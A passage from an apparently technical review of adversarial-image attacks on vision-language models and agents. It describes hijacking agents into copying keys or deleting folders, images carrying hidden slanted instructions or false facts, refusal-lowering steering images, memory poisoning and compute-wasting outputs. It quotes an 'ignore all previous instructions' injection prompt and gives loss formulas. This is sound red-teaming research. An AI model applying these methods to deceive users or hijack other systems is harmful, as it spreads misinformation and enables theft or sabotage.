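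These tests assumed that no icon covered the patch on the desktop and that the attacker's post was the first in the feed. The patch also failed on a version of Llama 3.2 Vision that wasn't used to train it. Aichberger and colleagues warn that a patch could make an agent share the post that contains it and so spread like a computer worm, but neither of their target programs did this.

### Does the action actually happen?

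Most of these studies count an attack as successful when the model writes the text the attacker wanted. Liu, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *AgentHijack*, also checked what happened to the computer afterwards. They placed a 700-by-500-pixel patch on web pages they controlled and had agents visit the pages while doing harmless tasks. The attacker's goals included copying the user's private login key to another folder, deleting a folder of course notes and stopping a VPN service. They tested five open models and trained each patch on the model it attacked.

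Across 600 cases, covering 15 goals, two kinds of page, four harmless tasks and the five models, Liu and colleagues found that:

- the model produced the target text in 84.5% of cases;
- the agent's parser recognised the target action in 47.0%;
- the computer ended up in the state the attacker wanted in 20.3%.

A model can therefore write the attacker's command without anything happening. The parser may reject the command, or the agent may type it into the wrong window or perform the steps in the wrong order. In this experiment, the agent had to open a terminal, a window for typing commands, before entering the harmful command. Aichberger and colleagues' agent could run a whole program from a single output, so fewer things could go wrong after it wrote the text. We can't use the 20.3% to estimate how often their attack would succeed, but it shows why a success rate for text alone can overstate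 the danger.

The rate might also be lower in ordinary use. All four harmless tasks already required the agent to open a terminal and write something, so the attack only had to change what the agent typed. An agent booking a hotel would have no reason to open a terminal. The agent also only copied the private key to another folder on the same machine, so an attacker would still need to get it off the machine.

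Some of the successful attacks would have been easy to miss because the agent ran the harmful command first and then went on with the user's task.

### Agents built on commercial models

All the agent attacks above relied on the weights of the main model. In *Dissecting Adversarial Robustness of Multimodal LM Agents*, Wu, Shah and colleagues (2024) attacked research agents that used commercial models, including OpenAI's GPT-4V and GPT-4o. They wrote 200 attack tasks for a test environment with a shopping site, a forum and a classified-ads site. The attacker was an ordinary seller or poster who could change only his own picture, which took up less than 5% of the page. His goal might be to make the agent add his product to the user's basket or give the user a false price. Wu and colleagues counted an attack as successful only if the agent achieved the attacker's goal.

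The easiest attack targeted the captioner, a smaller model that many web agents use to describe each picture in words for the main model. The captioner in these agents was open-weight, so the attacker could optimise a picture to produce a false caption, which the commercial model then received as text. With GPT-4o as the main model, 92% of the captions carried the attacker's message and 31% of the attacks reached their goal. With GPT-4V, 67% of the attacks succeeded.

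When the agent didn't use the open captioner, Wu and colleagues optimised the pictures on several versions of CLIP, hoping they would also affect GPT-4o. The attack succeeded 19% of the time when GPT-4o wrote its own captions and 10% when the agent used no captions. A seller who instead wrote instructions in his product description succeeded 40% of the time against GPT-4o.

Having the agent check its own work could make attacks more likely to succeed. Some agents have an evaluator, a second model call that reviews what the agent has done and can prompt it to try again. The attack success rate against the GPT-4o agent fell from 31% to 25% when the evaluator received an accurate caption, but rose to 36% when the evaluator also received the false caption. In that case, the evaluator approved more of the attacker's actions and rejected some correct ones.

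Wu and colleagues started each run on the page that contained the attacker's picture, so these rates apply only to agents that have already reached it. They also used only tasks that their best agent could complete without an attack. GPT-4V and GPT-4o date from 2023 and 2024, so newer commercial models may respond differently. The agents were research systems, and neither Wu and colleagues nor the groups that attacked open models report using optimised pixels against a deployed product.

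*Are GUI Agents Focused Enough?* (2026) describes an attack that adds decoy icons to screenshots so that agents click in the wrong place. In one example, a newer commercial model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, misses the correct button on a Windows screen. But the user could see the icons too, and a misplaced click gives an attacker much less than a command of his choice would.

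## Can an image stand in for a hidden text instruction?

An attacker who wants one exact sentence or tool call can train an image to make the model output that text. But to spread a political slant or a false claim, the attacker needs answers that vary with the user's questions, as they would if an instruction like "give every answer a positive spin" came before the user's message. A third-party attacker can't type into the conversation, so the image must have the same effect as the typed instruction.

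### Matching the prompt's embedding

The most direct approach works on the vectors that enter the language model. Since models like LLaVA process image tokens and word embeddings in the same way, an image that produced the same vectors as a written prompt would have the same effect as the prompt. The attacker would therefore look for an image x such that

E(x) ≈ T(p)

where p is the secret prompt, T(p) is its sequence of word embeddings and E(x) is the sequence of image tokens. He wouldn't even need to run the language model, because the loss is just the distance between the two sides.

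In 2023, Bagdasaryan and colleagues tried and failed to make an image stand in for a hidden text instruction. Bailey and colleagues also failed in informal experiments. They couldn't move an image's embedding close enough to the prompt's to meaningfully change the model's behaviour.

Both groups blame the modality gap. Liang, Zhang and colleagues (2022) introduced the term in *Mind the Gap* for a pattern they found in CLIP and similar models. CLIP's developers trained its image encoder and text encoder together so that a photograph and its caption would receive similar vectors. Yet the image vectors and the text vectors lay in two completely separate regions. CLIP scales every vector to length 1, so they all lie on a sphere of radius 1. For 5,000 photographs and their captions, the centre of the image vectors was 0.82 from the centre of the text vectors.

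Liang and colleagues trace the gap to the way neural networks start out. An encoder with random weights already maps all its inputs into a narrow cone, even if the inputs are random noise. Two encoders with different starting weights have different cones, and training doesn't merge them. One half of CLIP's loss, which matches images to captions, shows why it needn't:

L = − (1/N) Σ_i log [ exp(x_i · y_i / τ) / Σ_j exp(x_i · y_j / τ) ]

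Here x_i and y_i are the vectors of the i-th image and its caption, N is the number of pairs in the batch, and τ is a scaling factor. The loss falls when an image becomes more similar to its own caption than to the other captions. If an image's similarity to every caption dropped by the same amount, the fraction would stay the same, so the loss can be low even while the image and caption vectors remain apart. The cause of this gap is still in dispute. *Decipher the Modality Gap in Multimodal Contrastive Learning* (2025) lists rival explanations, including insufficient training and mismatched image-caption pairs. *On the modality gap and the contrastive loss in multi-modal representation learning* (2026) reports that CLIP-style models often still have a pronounced gap.

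Besides the gap within CLIP, the attacker has to match the word embeddings of a different model, because LLaVA uses CLIP's image encoder but not its text encoder. Bagdasaryan and colleagues use "modality gap" for this wider mismatch between components that nobody trained to produce similar vectors. They claim that no image produces an embedding close to the prompt's. The evidence doesn't establish this, because Liang and colleagues measured the embeddings of ordinary photographs, and an optimised image's embedding may lie elsewhere.

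A close match would also cause problems. The prompt may need more vectors than the image supplies. PandaGPT's encoder, for example, turns a whole picture into one vector, the same size as a single token's vector in the language model. And if all the image's vectors matched the prompt's, they would no longer carry information about the picture, so the model couldn't answer the user's questions about it.

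Bagdasaryan and colleagues worked around this gap by training the image to make the model write the instruction itself. The model's first answer includes a sentence saying it will always follow the attacker's instruction. That sentence stays in the chatbot's context, so the model follows the instruction in later answers. However, the user can also read the instruction.

### Prompt Matching

Bailey and colleagues dropped the requirement that the image resemble the prompt inside the model and asked only that it lead to the same output. They call this method Prompt Matching. Its goal is an image x that satisfies

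M(x, ctx) ≈ M(I, p + ctx) for every context ctx

where M gives the model's output logits, I is an ordinary image, and p + ctx is the secret prompt followed by the user's text. The right-hand side is what the model would do if the attacker could type the prompt. The attacker can use it as the target behaviour B in Behaviour Matching. The procedure is:

1. Write the secret prompt p and choose an ordinary image I.
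2. Collect a large set of generic instructions, which need have nothing to do with p.
3. For each instruction, run the model on I with p in front of the instruction. Record the answer and the logits at every position.
4. Train the image by Behaviour Matching on the same instructions without p, with the recorded logits as the target.

The model generates its own training data, so the attacker doesn't have to write example answers. This helped Bailey and colleagues when they tested a prompt telling LLaVA that the Eiffel Tower had moved to Rome. To teach the same thing by example, they would have had to write many questions whose answers depend on the tower's location and answer them all consistently.

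Bailey and colleagues trained on 82,000 prompts for up to 30,000 steps. The prompts were the 52,000 Alpaca instructions and 30,000 copies of ten variations on "Repeat your previous sentence". They don't say why they added the repeat requests, but it was probably to get the wording of the secret prompt into the targets. When the secret prompt comes just before such a request, it is the previous sentence, so the recorded answer should quote it. To match that answer, the image has to make the model quote a sentence that appears nowhere in its text input. The ten requests would work equally well with any other secret prompt, so the data don't depend on the attacker's message.

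The best image, made with no limit on pixel changes, led the model to give answers consistent with the move to Rome on 85% of 20 test questions, compared with 100% for the typed prompt.

### Why match logits rather than text?

The attacker could record only the text of each answer in step 3 and train the image on that. Bailey and colleagues argue that this text would provide too little information about the secret prompt, because the prompt leaves most answers unchanged. Asked "What is the capital of the United States?", the model names Washington whether or not the prompt includes the claim that the Eiffel Tower is in Rome. The model already gives that answer with an unmodified photograph, so the text of this example provides no information about the prompt.

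The logits can differ even when the text doesn't. Suppose that the secret prompt raises the probability of "Rome" as the first word of the answer from 0.0001 to 0.002, while "Washington" stays above 0.99. The gradient of the cross-entropy with respect to the logit of a token v is

∂L/∂z_v = p_v − q_v

where p_v is the probability the model gives the token with the image, and q_v is the target probability. If the target is the text alone, q is 0 for "Rome" and the gradient is 0.0001 − 0 = 0.0001. A positive gradient means that the optimiser lowers the logit, so training on text would push "Rome" slightly further down. If the target is the full set of probabilities, the gradient is 0.0001 − 0.002 = −0.0019, and the optimiser pushes "Rome" up. The same applies to the other tokens in the vocabulary, at every position in the answer.

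The argument comes from knowledge distillation, which trains a small network to imitate a large one. In *Distilling the Knowledge in a Neural Network*, Hinton, Vinyals and Dean (2015) trained the small network on the large one's probabilities, called soft targets, as well as the correct labels. A picture of a BMW has only a tiny chance of being mistaken for a garbage truck, but that is still many times more likely than its being mistaken for a carrot. The ratio between those small probabilities shows how the large network generalises, information that the correct label alone doesn't contain.

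One of their experiments is close to what Prompt Matching requires. They trained a small network to recognise handwritten digits from a large network's soft targets, but removed every 3 from the training examples. After they corrected a single bias term, the small network recognised 98.6% of the 3s in the test set. It had learned what a 3 looks like from the small probabilities that the large network gave to "3" for other digits. Similarly, training on questions that never mention the Eiffel Tower might still encode a claim about it in an image. In Prompt Matching, however, the same model serves as both networks, and training changes only the image's pixels.

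The capital-city question is a hard case even for soft targets. Hinton and colleagues say that soft targets are most informative when they are spread over many options, and that probabilities close to zero have very little influence on the cross-entropy. They therefore divide all the logits by a constant, the temperature, before computing the probabilities, which makes the small ones larger. Bailey and colleagues don't describe doing this. Open-ended instructions, where many next words are plausible, and the requests to repeat the previous sentence may have contributed more to training their image. They also don't report training an image on the recorded text alone, so how much the logits contributed is unknown.

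### Training on answers that already have the slant

Zhang, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Self-interpreting Adversarial Images*, use a different source of training data. They aim to make an image carry a meta-instruction, a hidden instruction that sets the slant or style of the model's answers while it still answers questions about the picture. For example, a stock chart might lead the model to describe the company's prospects favourably, whatever the user asks.

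They define success by two conditions. If y is the model's answer to question p about picture x, and z is the property the attacker wants, then

α(y, z) = 1 and β(p, x, y) = 1

An answer meets the first condition if it has the property, such as a positive tone, and the second if it responds appropriately to the question and the picture. An ordinary answer would usually fail the first condition, and the malware.com sentence would fail the second for almost any question.

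To train an image, Zhang and colleagues gave ChatGPT a picture with a label for its content and had it write 100 questions a user might ask about the picture. ChatGPT then answered those questions in line with the meta-instruction. A separate program, usually a text classifier, checked whether the answers had the intended property. If fewer than 80% did, the researchers generated a new set. They used 40% of the question-answer pairs to optimise the image with PGD and kept the rest for testing.

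Plain text targets, without logits, are enough here because each example answer is meant to show the slant, whereas most of the answers in Prompt Matching show no visible trace of the secret prompt. This method also uses far less data, with 40 pairs per picture compared with 82,000 prompts for Prompt Matching.

Zhang and colleagues describe the result as a soft prompt, a sequence of continuous vectors that takes the place of word embeddings. Developers use soft prompts to adapt language models. An outsider normally can't feed vectors directly into someone else's model, but can do so indirectly through an image. The vectors don't have to match those of any real sentence, so the modality gap doesn't prevent this.

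### How well do meta-instructions work?

In the main experiment, Zhang and colleagues tested MiniGPT-4, LLaVA and InstructBLIP, three open models from 2023, with full access to their weights. They used 15 photographs, changed each pixel value by at most 32/255 of its full range, and ran 2,000 iterations. They tried 12 objectives: positive, negative or neutral sentiment; formal or informal style; English, French or Spanish; a Republican or Democratic slant; and the insertion of an advertisement or a web address.

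The next table gives the sentiment and political results. Each cell lists the share of answers with the chosen property, first for an unmodified picture, then for an unmodified picture with an explicit text instruction, and last for the trained image without any instruction.

| Objective | MiniGPT-4 | LLaVA | InstructBLIP |
|---|---|---|---|
| Positive | 18% / 61% / 44% | 13% / 68% / 41% | 11% / 36% / 43% |
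| Negative | 16% / 16% / 33% | 3% / 25% / 5% | 26% / 2% / 18% |
| Neutral | 66% / 78% / 70% | 84% / 82% / 85% | 63% / 69% / 83% |
| Republican slant | 0% / 22% / 45% | 0% / 27% / 18% | 0% / 13% / 27% |
| Democratic slant | 0% / 15% / 38% | 0% / 37% / 15% | 0% / 10% / 37% |

The positive and political images clearly affected all three models. The political results are more striking because no model showed either slant without an attack, though even in the best case fewer than half of the answers were slanted. The neutral results are less informative because most answers were neutral anyway.

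Negative sentiment was much harder to produce. On LLaVA, images trained on that model raised the share of negative answers only from 3% to 5%. On InstructBLIP, the images lowered it from 26% to 18%, and the text instruction lowered it even further. Images can probably do better than 5% on LLaVA, because those that Zhang and colleagues had trained on MiniGPT-4 produced negative answers there 12% of the time. The comparison is slightly uneven, since they picked the best of ten saved versions of each transferred image.

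Zhang and colleagues say that images achieve results comparable to explicit text for all 12 meta-instructions, but on LLaVA, text did considerably better for positive and negative sentiment and for both political slants. On the other two models, the images often did better than text. However, each text instruction was a single plain request to answer with the given spin or bias, and a more carefully written prompt might have scored higher.

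The scores also depend on automatic judges. The sentiment classifier was trained on Twitter posts, which read differently from descriptions of photographs. ChatGPT judged whether an answer leaned left or right. No human readers rated the answers, so it's uncertain whether a user would notice the slant or be swayed by it. For the second condition, ChatGPT judged about 96% of the answers relevant to the question and the picture.

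Smaller changes to the picture weakened the effect. When each pixel value could change by at most 16/255, positive answers from MiniGPT-4 fell from 44% to 26% and negative ones from 33% to 27%. Zhang and colleagues also tried limiting the overall size of the change instead, measured as the square root of the sum of the squared pixel changes. With the loosest such limit, 83% of answers were positive.

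Writing the instruction on the image would not have worked with these three models, because they failed to recognise even black words on a white background. Models that read text well are more vulnerable to such instructions. *Text Prompt Injection of Vision Language Models* (2025) embeds a sentence in a photograph of a tiger, telling the model to act as if the photograph showed a cat. *Image-based Prompt Injection* (2026) describes an attack that needs no access to the model's weights and involves choosing where to place the words and how to blend them into the background.

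### What can each method express?

Prompt Matching can aim for anything the attacker can put into a prompt, including a false fact with many consequences. The attacker can reuse the same generic instructions for each new prompt. These are ordinary text requests, so the method doesn't specifically target what the model says about the picture.

The question-answer method suits properties that show up in nearly every answer, such as tone or language. It needs new data for each picture and each objective, but another model can write that data in bulk. This weakens one of the reasons for Prompt Matching, which is that a person would find it laborious to write thousands of answers that place the Eiffel Tower in Rome. But Zhang and colleagues did not test false facts like this, so we don't know whether 40 examples would be enough to make a model apply one consistently.

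Both groups say Prompt Matching is limited by the text prompt it imitates. According to Bailey and colleagues, the image can perform no better than the typed prompt. Zhang and colleagues go further and claim that their own images can bring out answers the model never gives to text prompts. They say Prompt Matching can't do this because its targets are the model's responses to text. Their example answers come from ChatGPT, so the target model doesn't have to be able to follow the instruction when it is given as text. With LLaVA, a text request for Spanish worked 1% of the time, while the images worked 21% of the time.

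An image that matched the recorded logits perfectly would behave exactly like the prompt, and further training could not improve it. An imperfect image, however, may score higher or lower than the prompt on a particular test. The limit set by the prompt also depends on its wording, so if one wording fails, the attacker can look for another before training the image. Zhang and colleagues did not run Prompt Matching on their 12 objectives, so their experiments don't show how much this limit matters in practice.

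Lan, Cao and colleagues (2025), in *Phi*, compared their method with Bailey and colleagues' images on LLaVA-1.5 and the newer Llama 3.2 Vision. These baseline images were probably made with Prompt Matching, since the paper attributes their low scores to the weakness of text prompts on the same tasks. In one test, the attacker wanted critical comments about a photograph of a city. Llama chose the critical answer from two options 2% of the time with the clean photograph, 50% with a text instruction and 6% with the baseline image. On some other tasks the baseline image did better than the text instruction, so if the two used the same prompt, the text instruction's score is not the upper bound it was supposed to be.

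Lan and colleagues' own image scored 100% on the city test. They trained it on pairs of answers to the same question, one with the attacker's slant and one with the opposite slant. The loss is

−log σ( log [ f(r_t | x + h, q) / f(r_t | x, q) ] − β · log [ f(r_o | x + h, q) / f(r_o | x, q) ] )

where f is the probability the model gives to an answer, q is the question, x is the clean image and h is the change to its pixels. The slanted answer is r_t, the opposite answer is r_o, σ is the sigmoid function, and β sets the weight of the second term. The loss falls when the changed image makes the slanted answer likelier and the opposite answer less likely. Zhang and colleagues' loss only does the first of these.

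Lan and colleagues argue that Prompt Matching and meta-instructions work only to the extent that the target model can and will follow instructions. This criticism applies less to meta-instructions, because Zhang and colleagues take their example answers from ChatGPT, not from the target model. Their method still depends on whether ChatGPT will write those answers. Lan and colleagues avoid this limit by using answers written by people or by models without safety training.

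An attacker can also train an image to produce chosen activations inside the model. Balakrishnan and Phute (2025), in *VISOR++*, start from a steering vector, which is the difference between a model's internal activations when it shows a behaviour and when it doesn't. Adding this vector while the model runs shifts its behaviour, but requires control of the running model. They instead trained images, with no limit on the pixels, to produce the activations that a plain grey image would produce with the vector added. The test questions offered one answer that refused a request and one that complied. With no steering, LLaVA-1.5 gave the refusing answer an average probability of 64%. The image lowered this to 42% and the steering vector lowered it to 33%, while with a text instruction to comply it was 70%.

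Hidden instructions can also be conditional. Bai, Ren and colleagues (2026), in *Answer It or Not?*, trained images to stop VLMs from answering questions that invade the privacy of people in a photograph. Earlier protective images made the model refuse every question. Theirs made it refuse more than 90% of the harmful questions and still allowed more than 90% of the legitimate ones.

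## Can an image make a model assert a chosen falsehood?

An attacker can make a VLM output a false statement in two ways. One is to change the information that reaches the language model from the visual encoder, so that the model describes a dog in a photograph as a cat. The other is to change the model's answers about the world, so that it places the Eiffel Tower in Rome whatever the photograph shows. Small pixel changes have been enough to alter the visual information. Changing a fact has taken much larger ones, although the evidence comes from a single experiment on a single fact.

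### Changing what the model sees

Schlarmann and Hein's 2023 attack on OpenFlamingo could spread false news as well as phishing messages. They altered ordinary photographs to make the model caption them "A person suffers severe side effects after vaccination". After 500 iterations per image, the full sentence appeared in 4% of captions at a budget of 1/255 and in 84% at 4/255. OpenFlamingo can also take a few captioned example pictures before the one it describes. When they altered four such examples as well, the rates rose to 23% and 100%.

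Schlarmann and Hein used the same captioning prompt to make and test the images, so a high score doesn't show that the model's answers would stay consistent with the false caption if a user asked a different question, such as whether anyone in the photograph looks ill.

Zhang, Narayan and Sarkar (2026), in *It Takes Little to Rewrite Perception*, tested this kind of consistency on Qwen3-VL. They took 469 pairs of photographs covering 102 kinds of object and altered the first picture in each pair so that the model would see the object in the second. They then asked four questions, each in a new conversation:

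- What is the main object?
- What does the picture show, in one sentence?
- Is the new object in the picture?
- Is the original object in the picture?

A replacement counted as complete only if the model named the new object, answered that it was present and answered that the original was not. The score excluded the one-sentence description because it depended on which object the model treated as the main one.

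One of their attacks trained each image in the usual way, by raising the probability of the new object's name as the answer to the question about the main object. It achieved complete replacement about 24% of the time at a perturbation budget of 4/255, and quadrupling the budget didn't help. The model often gave the new name when asked the trained question but still confirmed that the original object was there, which the loss didn't penalize.

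Their own method, TokRA, ignores the model's answers and works on the vectors that the language model receives. Qwen3-VL passes these on in four streams: the image tokens that sit beside the user's text, and three further sets of features that enter the early layers. TokRA minimises

L(x) = − (1/4N) Σ_s Σ_i cos( f_{s,i}(x), f_{s,i}(x_t) )

where x is the altered picture, x_t is the picture the attacker wants the model to see, and f_{s,i} is the vector at position i in stream s. N is the number of positions, and cos is the cosine similarity, which equals 1 when two vectors point in the same direction. The researchers resized both pictures to the same dimensions, so position i covers the same part of each. As a vector moves towards the cat's, it moves away from the dog's, so one loss both adds the new object and removes the old one.

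The table gives TokRA's results on Qwen3-VL and the older Qwen2.5-VL.

| Budget | Qwen3-VL confirms new object | Qwen3-VL, complete replacement | Qwen2.5-VL confirms new object | Qwen2.5-VL, complete replacement |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2/255 | 35.0% | 8.7% | 38.8% | 6.8% |
| 4/255 | 80.6% | 38.2% | 79.5% | 33.0% |
| 8/255 | 98.3% | 64.4% | 96.4% | 66.1% |

At 4/255, Qwen3-VL usually confirmed the new object, but in more than half of those cases it also confirmed the old one or named something else as the main object. Its descriptions often merged the two pictures. Given one altered photograph of a dog, it described the target picture's tabby cat lying on the original picture's sunlit stone steps. Such an answer may be more convincing than a complete swap, since much of it matches what the user can see.

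Videos needed even smaller changes than photographs. On 128 pairs of five-second clips, with a budget of 1/255, TokRA achieved complete replacement in 35.9%, and the model confirmed the new content in 70.3%. The same budget produced almost no complete replacements on photographs. The reason is unclear. The clips and photographs came from different datasets, and changing the number of frames the model sampled made little difference.

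These budgets are what an attack needs under ideal conditions. Zhang, Narayan and Sarkar had the model's weights, and they did not require the changes to survive compression or rescaling. For video, the attacker also has to alter exactly the frames the model will sample. Another language model, GPT-5.6 Sol, graded all the answers, and the researchers didn't check its grades against human ones. They report no result for LLaVA-1.5 because the attack had not converged after 500 steps.

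An attacker can do something similar using only the visual encoder. In *Breaking the weakest link to evade vision language models*, Zini, Addad and Kapusta (2026) minimised the squared distance between the encoder's outputs for the altered picture and a target picture. In their example, Granite-Vision-3.2-2B, a small open model, described a military tank as an ambulance. The perturbation limit was 0.05 of the pixel range, or about 13/255. The attack takes little compute because the encoder holds only 1.6% to 18% of the weights in the models they tested. It took about 100 seconds per image on Qwen2.5-VL, whereas an attack through the whole model ran for more than 20 minutes without success.

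To test more than the single tank example, Zini and colleagues randomly paired 1,000 photographs with target photographs and asked each model for a one-sentence description. A small language model judged whether the description matched the target.

| Budget | Granite-Vision-3.2-2B | FastVLM-7B | Qwen2.5-VL-3B | Phi-3.5-Vision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| About 13/255 | 41% | 26% | 9% | 2% |
| About 26/255 | 47% | 28% | 21% | 2% |
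| About 51/255 | 46% | 30% | 25% | 2% |

It was far easier to make a description wrong than to make it state a chosen falsehood. When Zini and colleagues only tried to push the encoder's output away from the original, they succeeded at least 93% of the time on every model.

The low targeted scores for Qwen2.5-VL and Phi-3.5 don't establish that those models are robust. Zini and colleagues ran only 50 iterations, and TokRA, with a smaller budget, completely replaced objects 66% of the time on a Qwen2.5-VL model. The two tests differ in that a description of a whole scene can miss its target in more ways than the name of an object can, but the gap is large enough to suggest that the choice of attack explains much of it.

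### What a changed picture can make a model claim

An attacker who controls what a model sees in an image can also influence its claims about things beyond the image. Zhang, Peetathawatchai and colleagues (2026), in *Laundering AI Authority with Adversarial Examples*, altered a photograph of a box of Tylenol, a common painkiller, so that a model would mistake it for Roaccutane, an acne drug that causes birth defects. When they asked whether it was safe during pregnancy, the model warned against it. That would have been good advice about Roaccutane, and nothing suggests that the model's knowledge of Tylenol had changed. A longer answer to a similar question revealed the attack by naming Roaccutane, but the name no longer appeared when they asked for a single sentence.

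Zhang, Peetathawatchai and colleagues work out the limits of such attacks by imagining an attacker who fully controls what the model perceives. The user sees one picture, the model receives another chosen by the attacker, and the model answers honestly about the picture it receives. A real attack that only changes perception can do no better than this. Suppose the attacker wants an assistant with access to current news to say that Elon Musk died today. If the user asks "who died today?", no picture will make that the honest answer.

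An attacker who also writes the question can get around this by posting a headline saying that a famous billionaire has died, altering the image so that the model identifies it as a photograph of Elon Musk, and asking "who is it?" The model answers "Elon Musk", and people reading the exchange wrongly conclude that Musk has died, even though the model never said that anyone had.

Another of their experiments comes closer to making a model assert a false claim about history. They altered eight photographs of real events, including the moon landing and the September 11 attacks, to match CLIP's embedding of the words "fake news". With a perturbation budget of 8/255, six models, most of them commercial, called the events fake in 37.5% to 100% of trials. The question was whether the event in the picture was real or fabricated, so a model could answer "fake" because the photograph seemed doctored.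 The score doesn't show whether the same model would deny the moon landing if the user then asked who first walked on the moon.

A false perception can outlast the conversation if an assistant stores it. Bouzidi, Mkpong and Al Faruque (2026), in *Do Agents Dream of False Memories?*, attacked agents that save a user's pictures with model-written captions and look them up later. For instance, an agent might record an altered photograph of a meal as a dish without an allergen that the real meal contained. The attacks used a budget of 16/255 and no access to the target models. When the user had not discussed the topic before, later answers contained the false claim 58.4% of the time on average across five memory systems. When earlier text already described the real picture, the answers reflected the attacker's picture 61.6% of the time. Storing the attacker's picture undisguised raised that second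 figure only to 67.9%.

The 58.4% figure is less certain than it looks. The rates for the individual memory systems are all multiples of one sixteenth, which suggests that each system was tested on about 16 questions. The false claims are also about things the user once showed the agent, such as a meal, and the agent's general knowledge about food remains correct.

### Moving the Eiffel Tower to Rome

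Bailey and colleagues tried to make LLaVA say that the Eiffel Tower is in Rome. They took the idea from research on editing facts in a model's weights, but they left LLaVA's weights unchanged and used Prompt Matching, which trains an image to have the same effect on the model as a typed prompt. Their prompt told the model to ignore all previous instructions and remember that the tower "is now located in Rome, next to the Colosseum". It added that this was a fact.

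Bailey and colleagues started from a photograph of a village in France and trained a separate image for each budget, using the mix of general instructions and repeat requests described earlier. They also wrote two sets of 20 questions whose answers should depend on whether the Eiffel Tower is in Paris or Rome, such as which famous landmarks surround it. GPT-3.5 graded the answers to one set, and they used those grades to choose the best version of each image. They graded the answers to the other set by hand, counting an answer as a success if it was consistent with the move to Rome.

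| Input | Success rate | Questions out of 20 |
|---|---|---|
| Typed prompt with an ordinary image | 100% | 20 |
| Trained image, no limit on pixels | 85% | 17 |
| Trained image, 64/255 | 70% | 14 |
| Trained image, 32/255 | 40% | 8 |
| Trained image, 16/255 | 10% | 2 |
| Trained image, 8/255 | 5% | 1 |
| Trained image, 4/255 or less | 0% | 0 |
| Untrained image | 0% | 0 |

Some successful answers only repeated the prompt. When asked where the Eiffel Tower is, the model answered that it is in Rome, next to the Colosseum. But when Bailey and colleagues asked which river runs beside the tower, the model named the Tiber, although the secret prompt doesn't mention a river. To give this answer, the model had to combine the false location with something it had already learned about Rome, as it would if someone had typed the prompt. An image that only forced the words "Rome" and "Colosseum" into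 every answer would not have produced "Tiber".

Bailey and colleagues describe this as modifying the model's knowledge, but the change lasts only while the image is in the context. It is closer to giving the model a false premise than to erasing its stored information about where the tower is.

With 20 questions, each answer is worth five percentage points. If we treat the questions as a random sample of all possible questions about the tower's location, the 95% confidence interval for the 85% result runs from about 64% to 95%. A score of zero is compatible with a true rate as high as 16%. The difference between 85% and 70% could easily be due to chance, but the fall from 70% at 64/255 to 5% at 8/255 could not.

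The edit should have changed the answers to all 20 questions, so the scores don't show how precise it was. An image that also made the model place the Louvre in Rome would have scored just as well. The experiment covers only one fact and one model. The Eiffel Tower is also unusually famous, so its location might be harder to override than an obscure fact, or easier because the model has so much information about it.

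The typed prompt's perfect score may also make the method look more effective than it is. *Believe It or Not* (2025), a text-only study of false facts in language models, found that prompts implanted such facts less well than training the model on them, especially when the facts were egregiously false. The 20 questions may have been too easy to reveal that weakness. Since the image imitates the prompt, it would probably also fail on harder questions that make the prompt fail.

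### Does rewriting a fact take a visible change?

Bailey and colleagues tried all three attacks on the same LLaVA model. When each pixel value could change by at most 8/255 of its range, they made the model output the malware.com sentence 99% of the time and leak the user's text 73% of the time, but they got only one of the 20 Eiffel Tower answers. To get most of those answers, they had to let each pixel value change by up to a quarter of its range, which is plainly visible in an ordinary photograph.

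The other studies fit this pattern. Attackers with access to a model's weights have altered what the model sees or forced it to output a fixed sentence, using image changes that most people would miss. Making a model apply a false fact consistently took visible changes. The boundary is not exact, because visibility depends on the picture. Zhang, Peetathawatchai and colleagues report that even changes of 4/255 or 8/255 can leave visible traces in a high-resolution image. They also needed 32/255 for the drug packages, probably because the models could read the printed names.

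The difference has two plausible explanations. An attacker who wants the model to see a cat knows that an image can produce the right vectors, because a photograph of the cat does. He only has to get close to those vectors while keeping the picture looking like a dog. No known photograph has the same effect as the Eiffel Tower prompt, and even with no limit on the pixels, the trained image was less effective than the prompt. The training signal is also weaker, because most of the training instructions have nothing to do with the tower. Bailey and colleagues didn't test these explanations separately.

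Newer attacks have produced false statements with small changes to the image, but none of those described here repeats the Eiffel Tower test. Schlarmann and Hein's "Apple iCar" images, for example, only had to produce the recommendation they were trained on. A comparable test would involve asking the model who designed the car or where to buy it, and checking that its answers agree with one another.

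The large budget may also reflect weaknesses in the attack more than the model's robustness. Bailey and colleagues used a learning rate of 3 for every Eiffel Tower image, a hundred times the rate they used for the malware.com images with small budgets. The two losses differ, so they may need different rates, but steps that are too large could easily spoil an image whose pixels can change only slightly. They also used a 2023 model and plain gradient descent. Zhang, Narayan and Sarkar point out that VLMs had seemed robust to object replacement at 4/255 until their attack aligned the image tokens position by position. A better way of training images to carry false facts might lower the required budget too.

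## Can an image make a model write far more than it should?

The attacks described so far are meant to control what a model writes. An attacker who only wants to waste a provider's computing power just needs the model to keep writing, whatever the wording. An image optimised for this purpose is called a verbose image.

### Why long outputs cost more

Each token that a VLM writes takes another pass through the language model. The model stops when it picks the end-of-sequence token, a special entry in its vocabulary, or when it reaches a limit set by the provider. Gao, Bai and colleagues (2024), in *Inducing High Energy-Latency of Large Vision-Language Models with Verbose Images*, measured four open VLMs and found that time and energy both rose roughly in a straight line with output length:

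cost ≈ a + b · N

Here N is the number of output tokens, b is the time or energy each one takes, and a is the time or energy needed to read the image and the prompt. For BLIP-2, one of the four models, a caption of nine tokens took an average of 0.4 seconds and 16 joules, and an output of 227 tokens took 8 seconds and 322 joules. These averages imply about 1.4 joules per token.

To get longer outputs, the attacker tries to make the end token less likely. If its probability were the same at every step, the average output length would be 1 divided by that probability, so cutting it from 2% to 0.2% would raise the average from 50 tokens to 500. In practice the probability is concentrated at the ends of sentences. Forcing a long output is still easier than forcing an exact string, because any long text will do.

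### Verbose Images, loss by loss

Gao and colleagues optimise the image with PGD, but without a target text. The model writes an answer to the current image, and they score that answer with three losses.

The first loss is the average probability of the end token over all N positions:

L₁(x) = (1/N) Σ_i p_i(end)

It covers every position because the model samples its words at random, so the attacker can't predict where the answer would have stopped.

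Lowering L₁ may not be enough. A model that writes its usual caption arrives at its usual last full stop, where the end token is hard to suppress. The other two losses push the model away from that caption. The second raises its uncertainty at each step:

L₂(x) = Σ_i KL( p_i ‖ U ) = Σ_i ( log V − H(p_i) )

KL is the Kullback–Leibler divergence, which measures how far one probability distribution is from another. U is the uniform distribution, which gives all V tokens in the vocabulary the same probability, and H(p_i) is the entropy of the model's prediction at position i. Since log V is fixed, lowering the loss raises the entropy, which makes the model more likely to pick tokens it would normally rarely pick.

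The third loss works on the hidden states, the vectors that the language model computes for each token as it writes:

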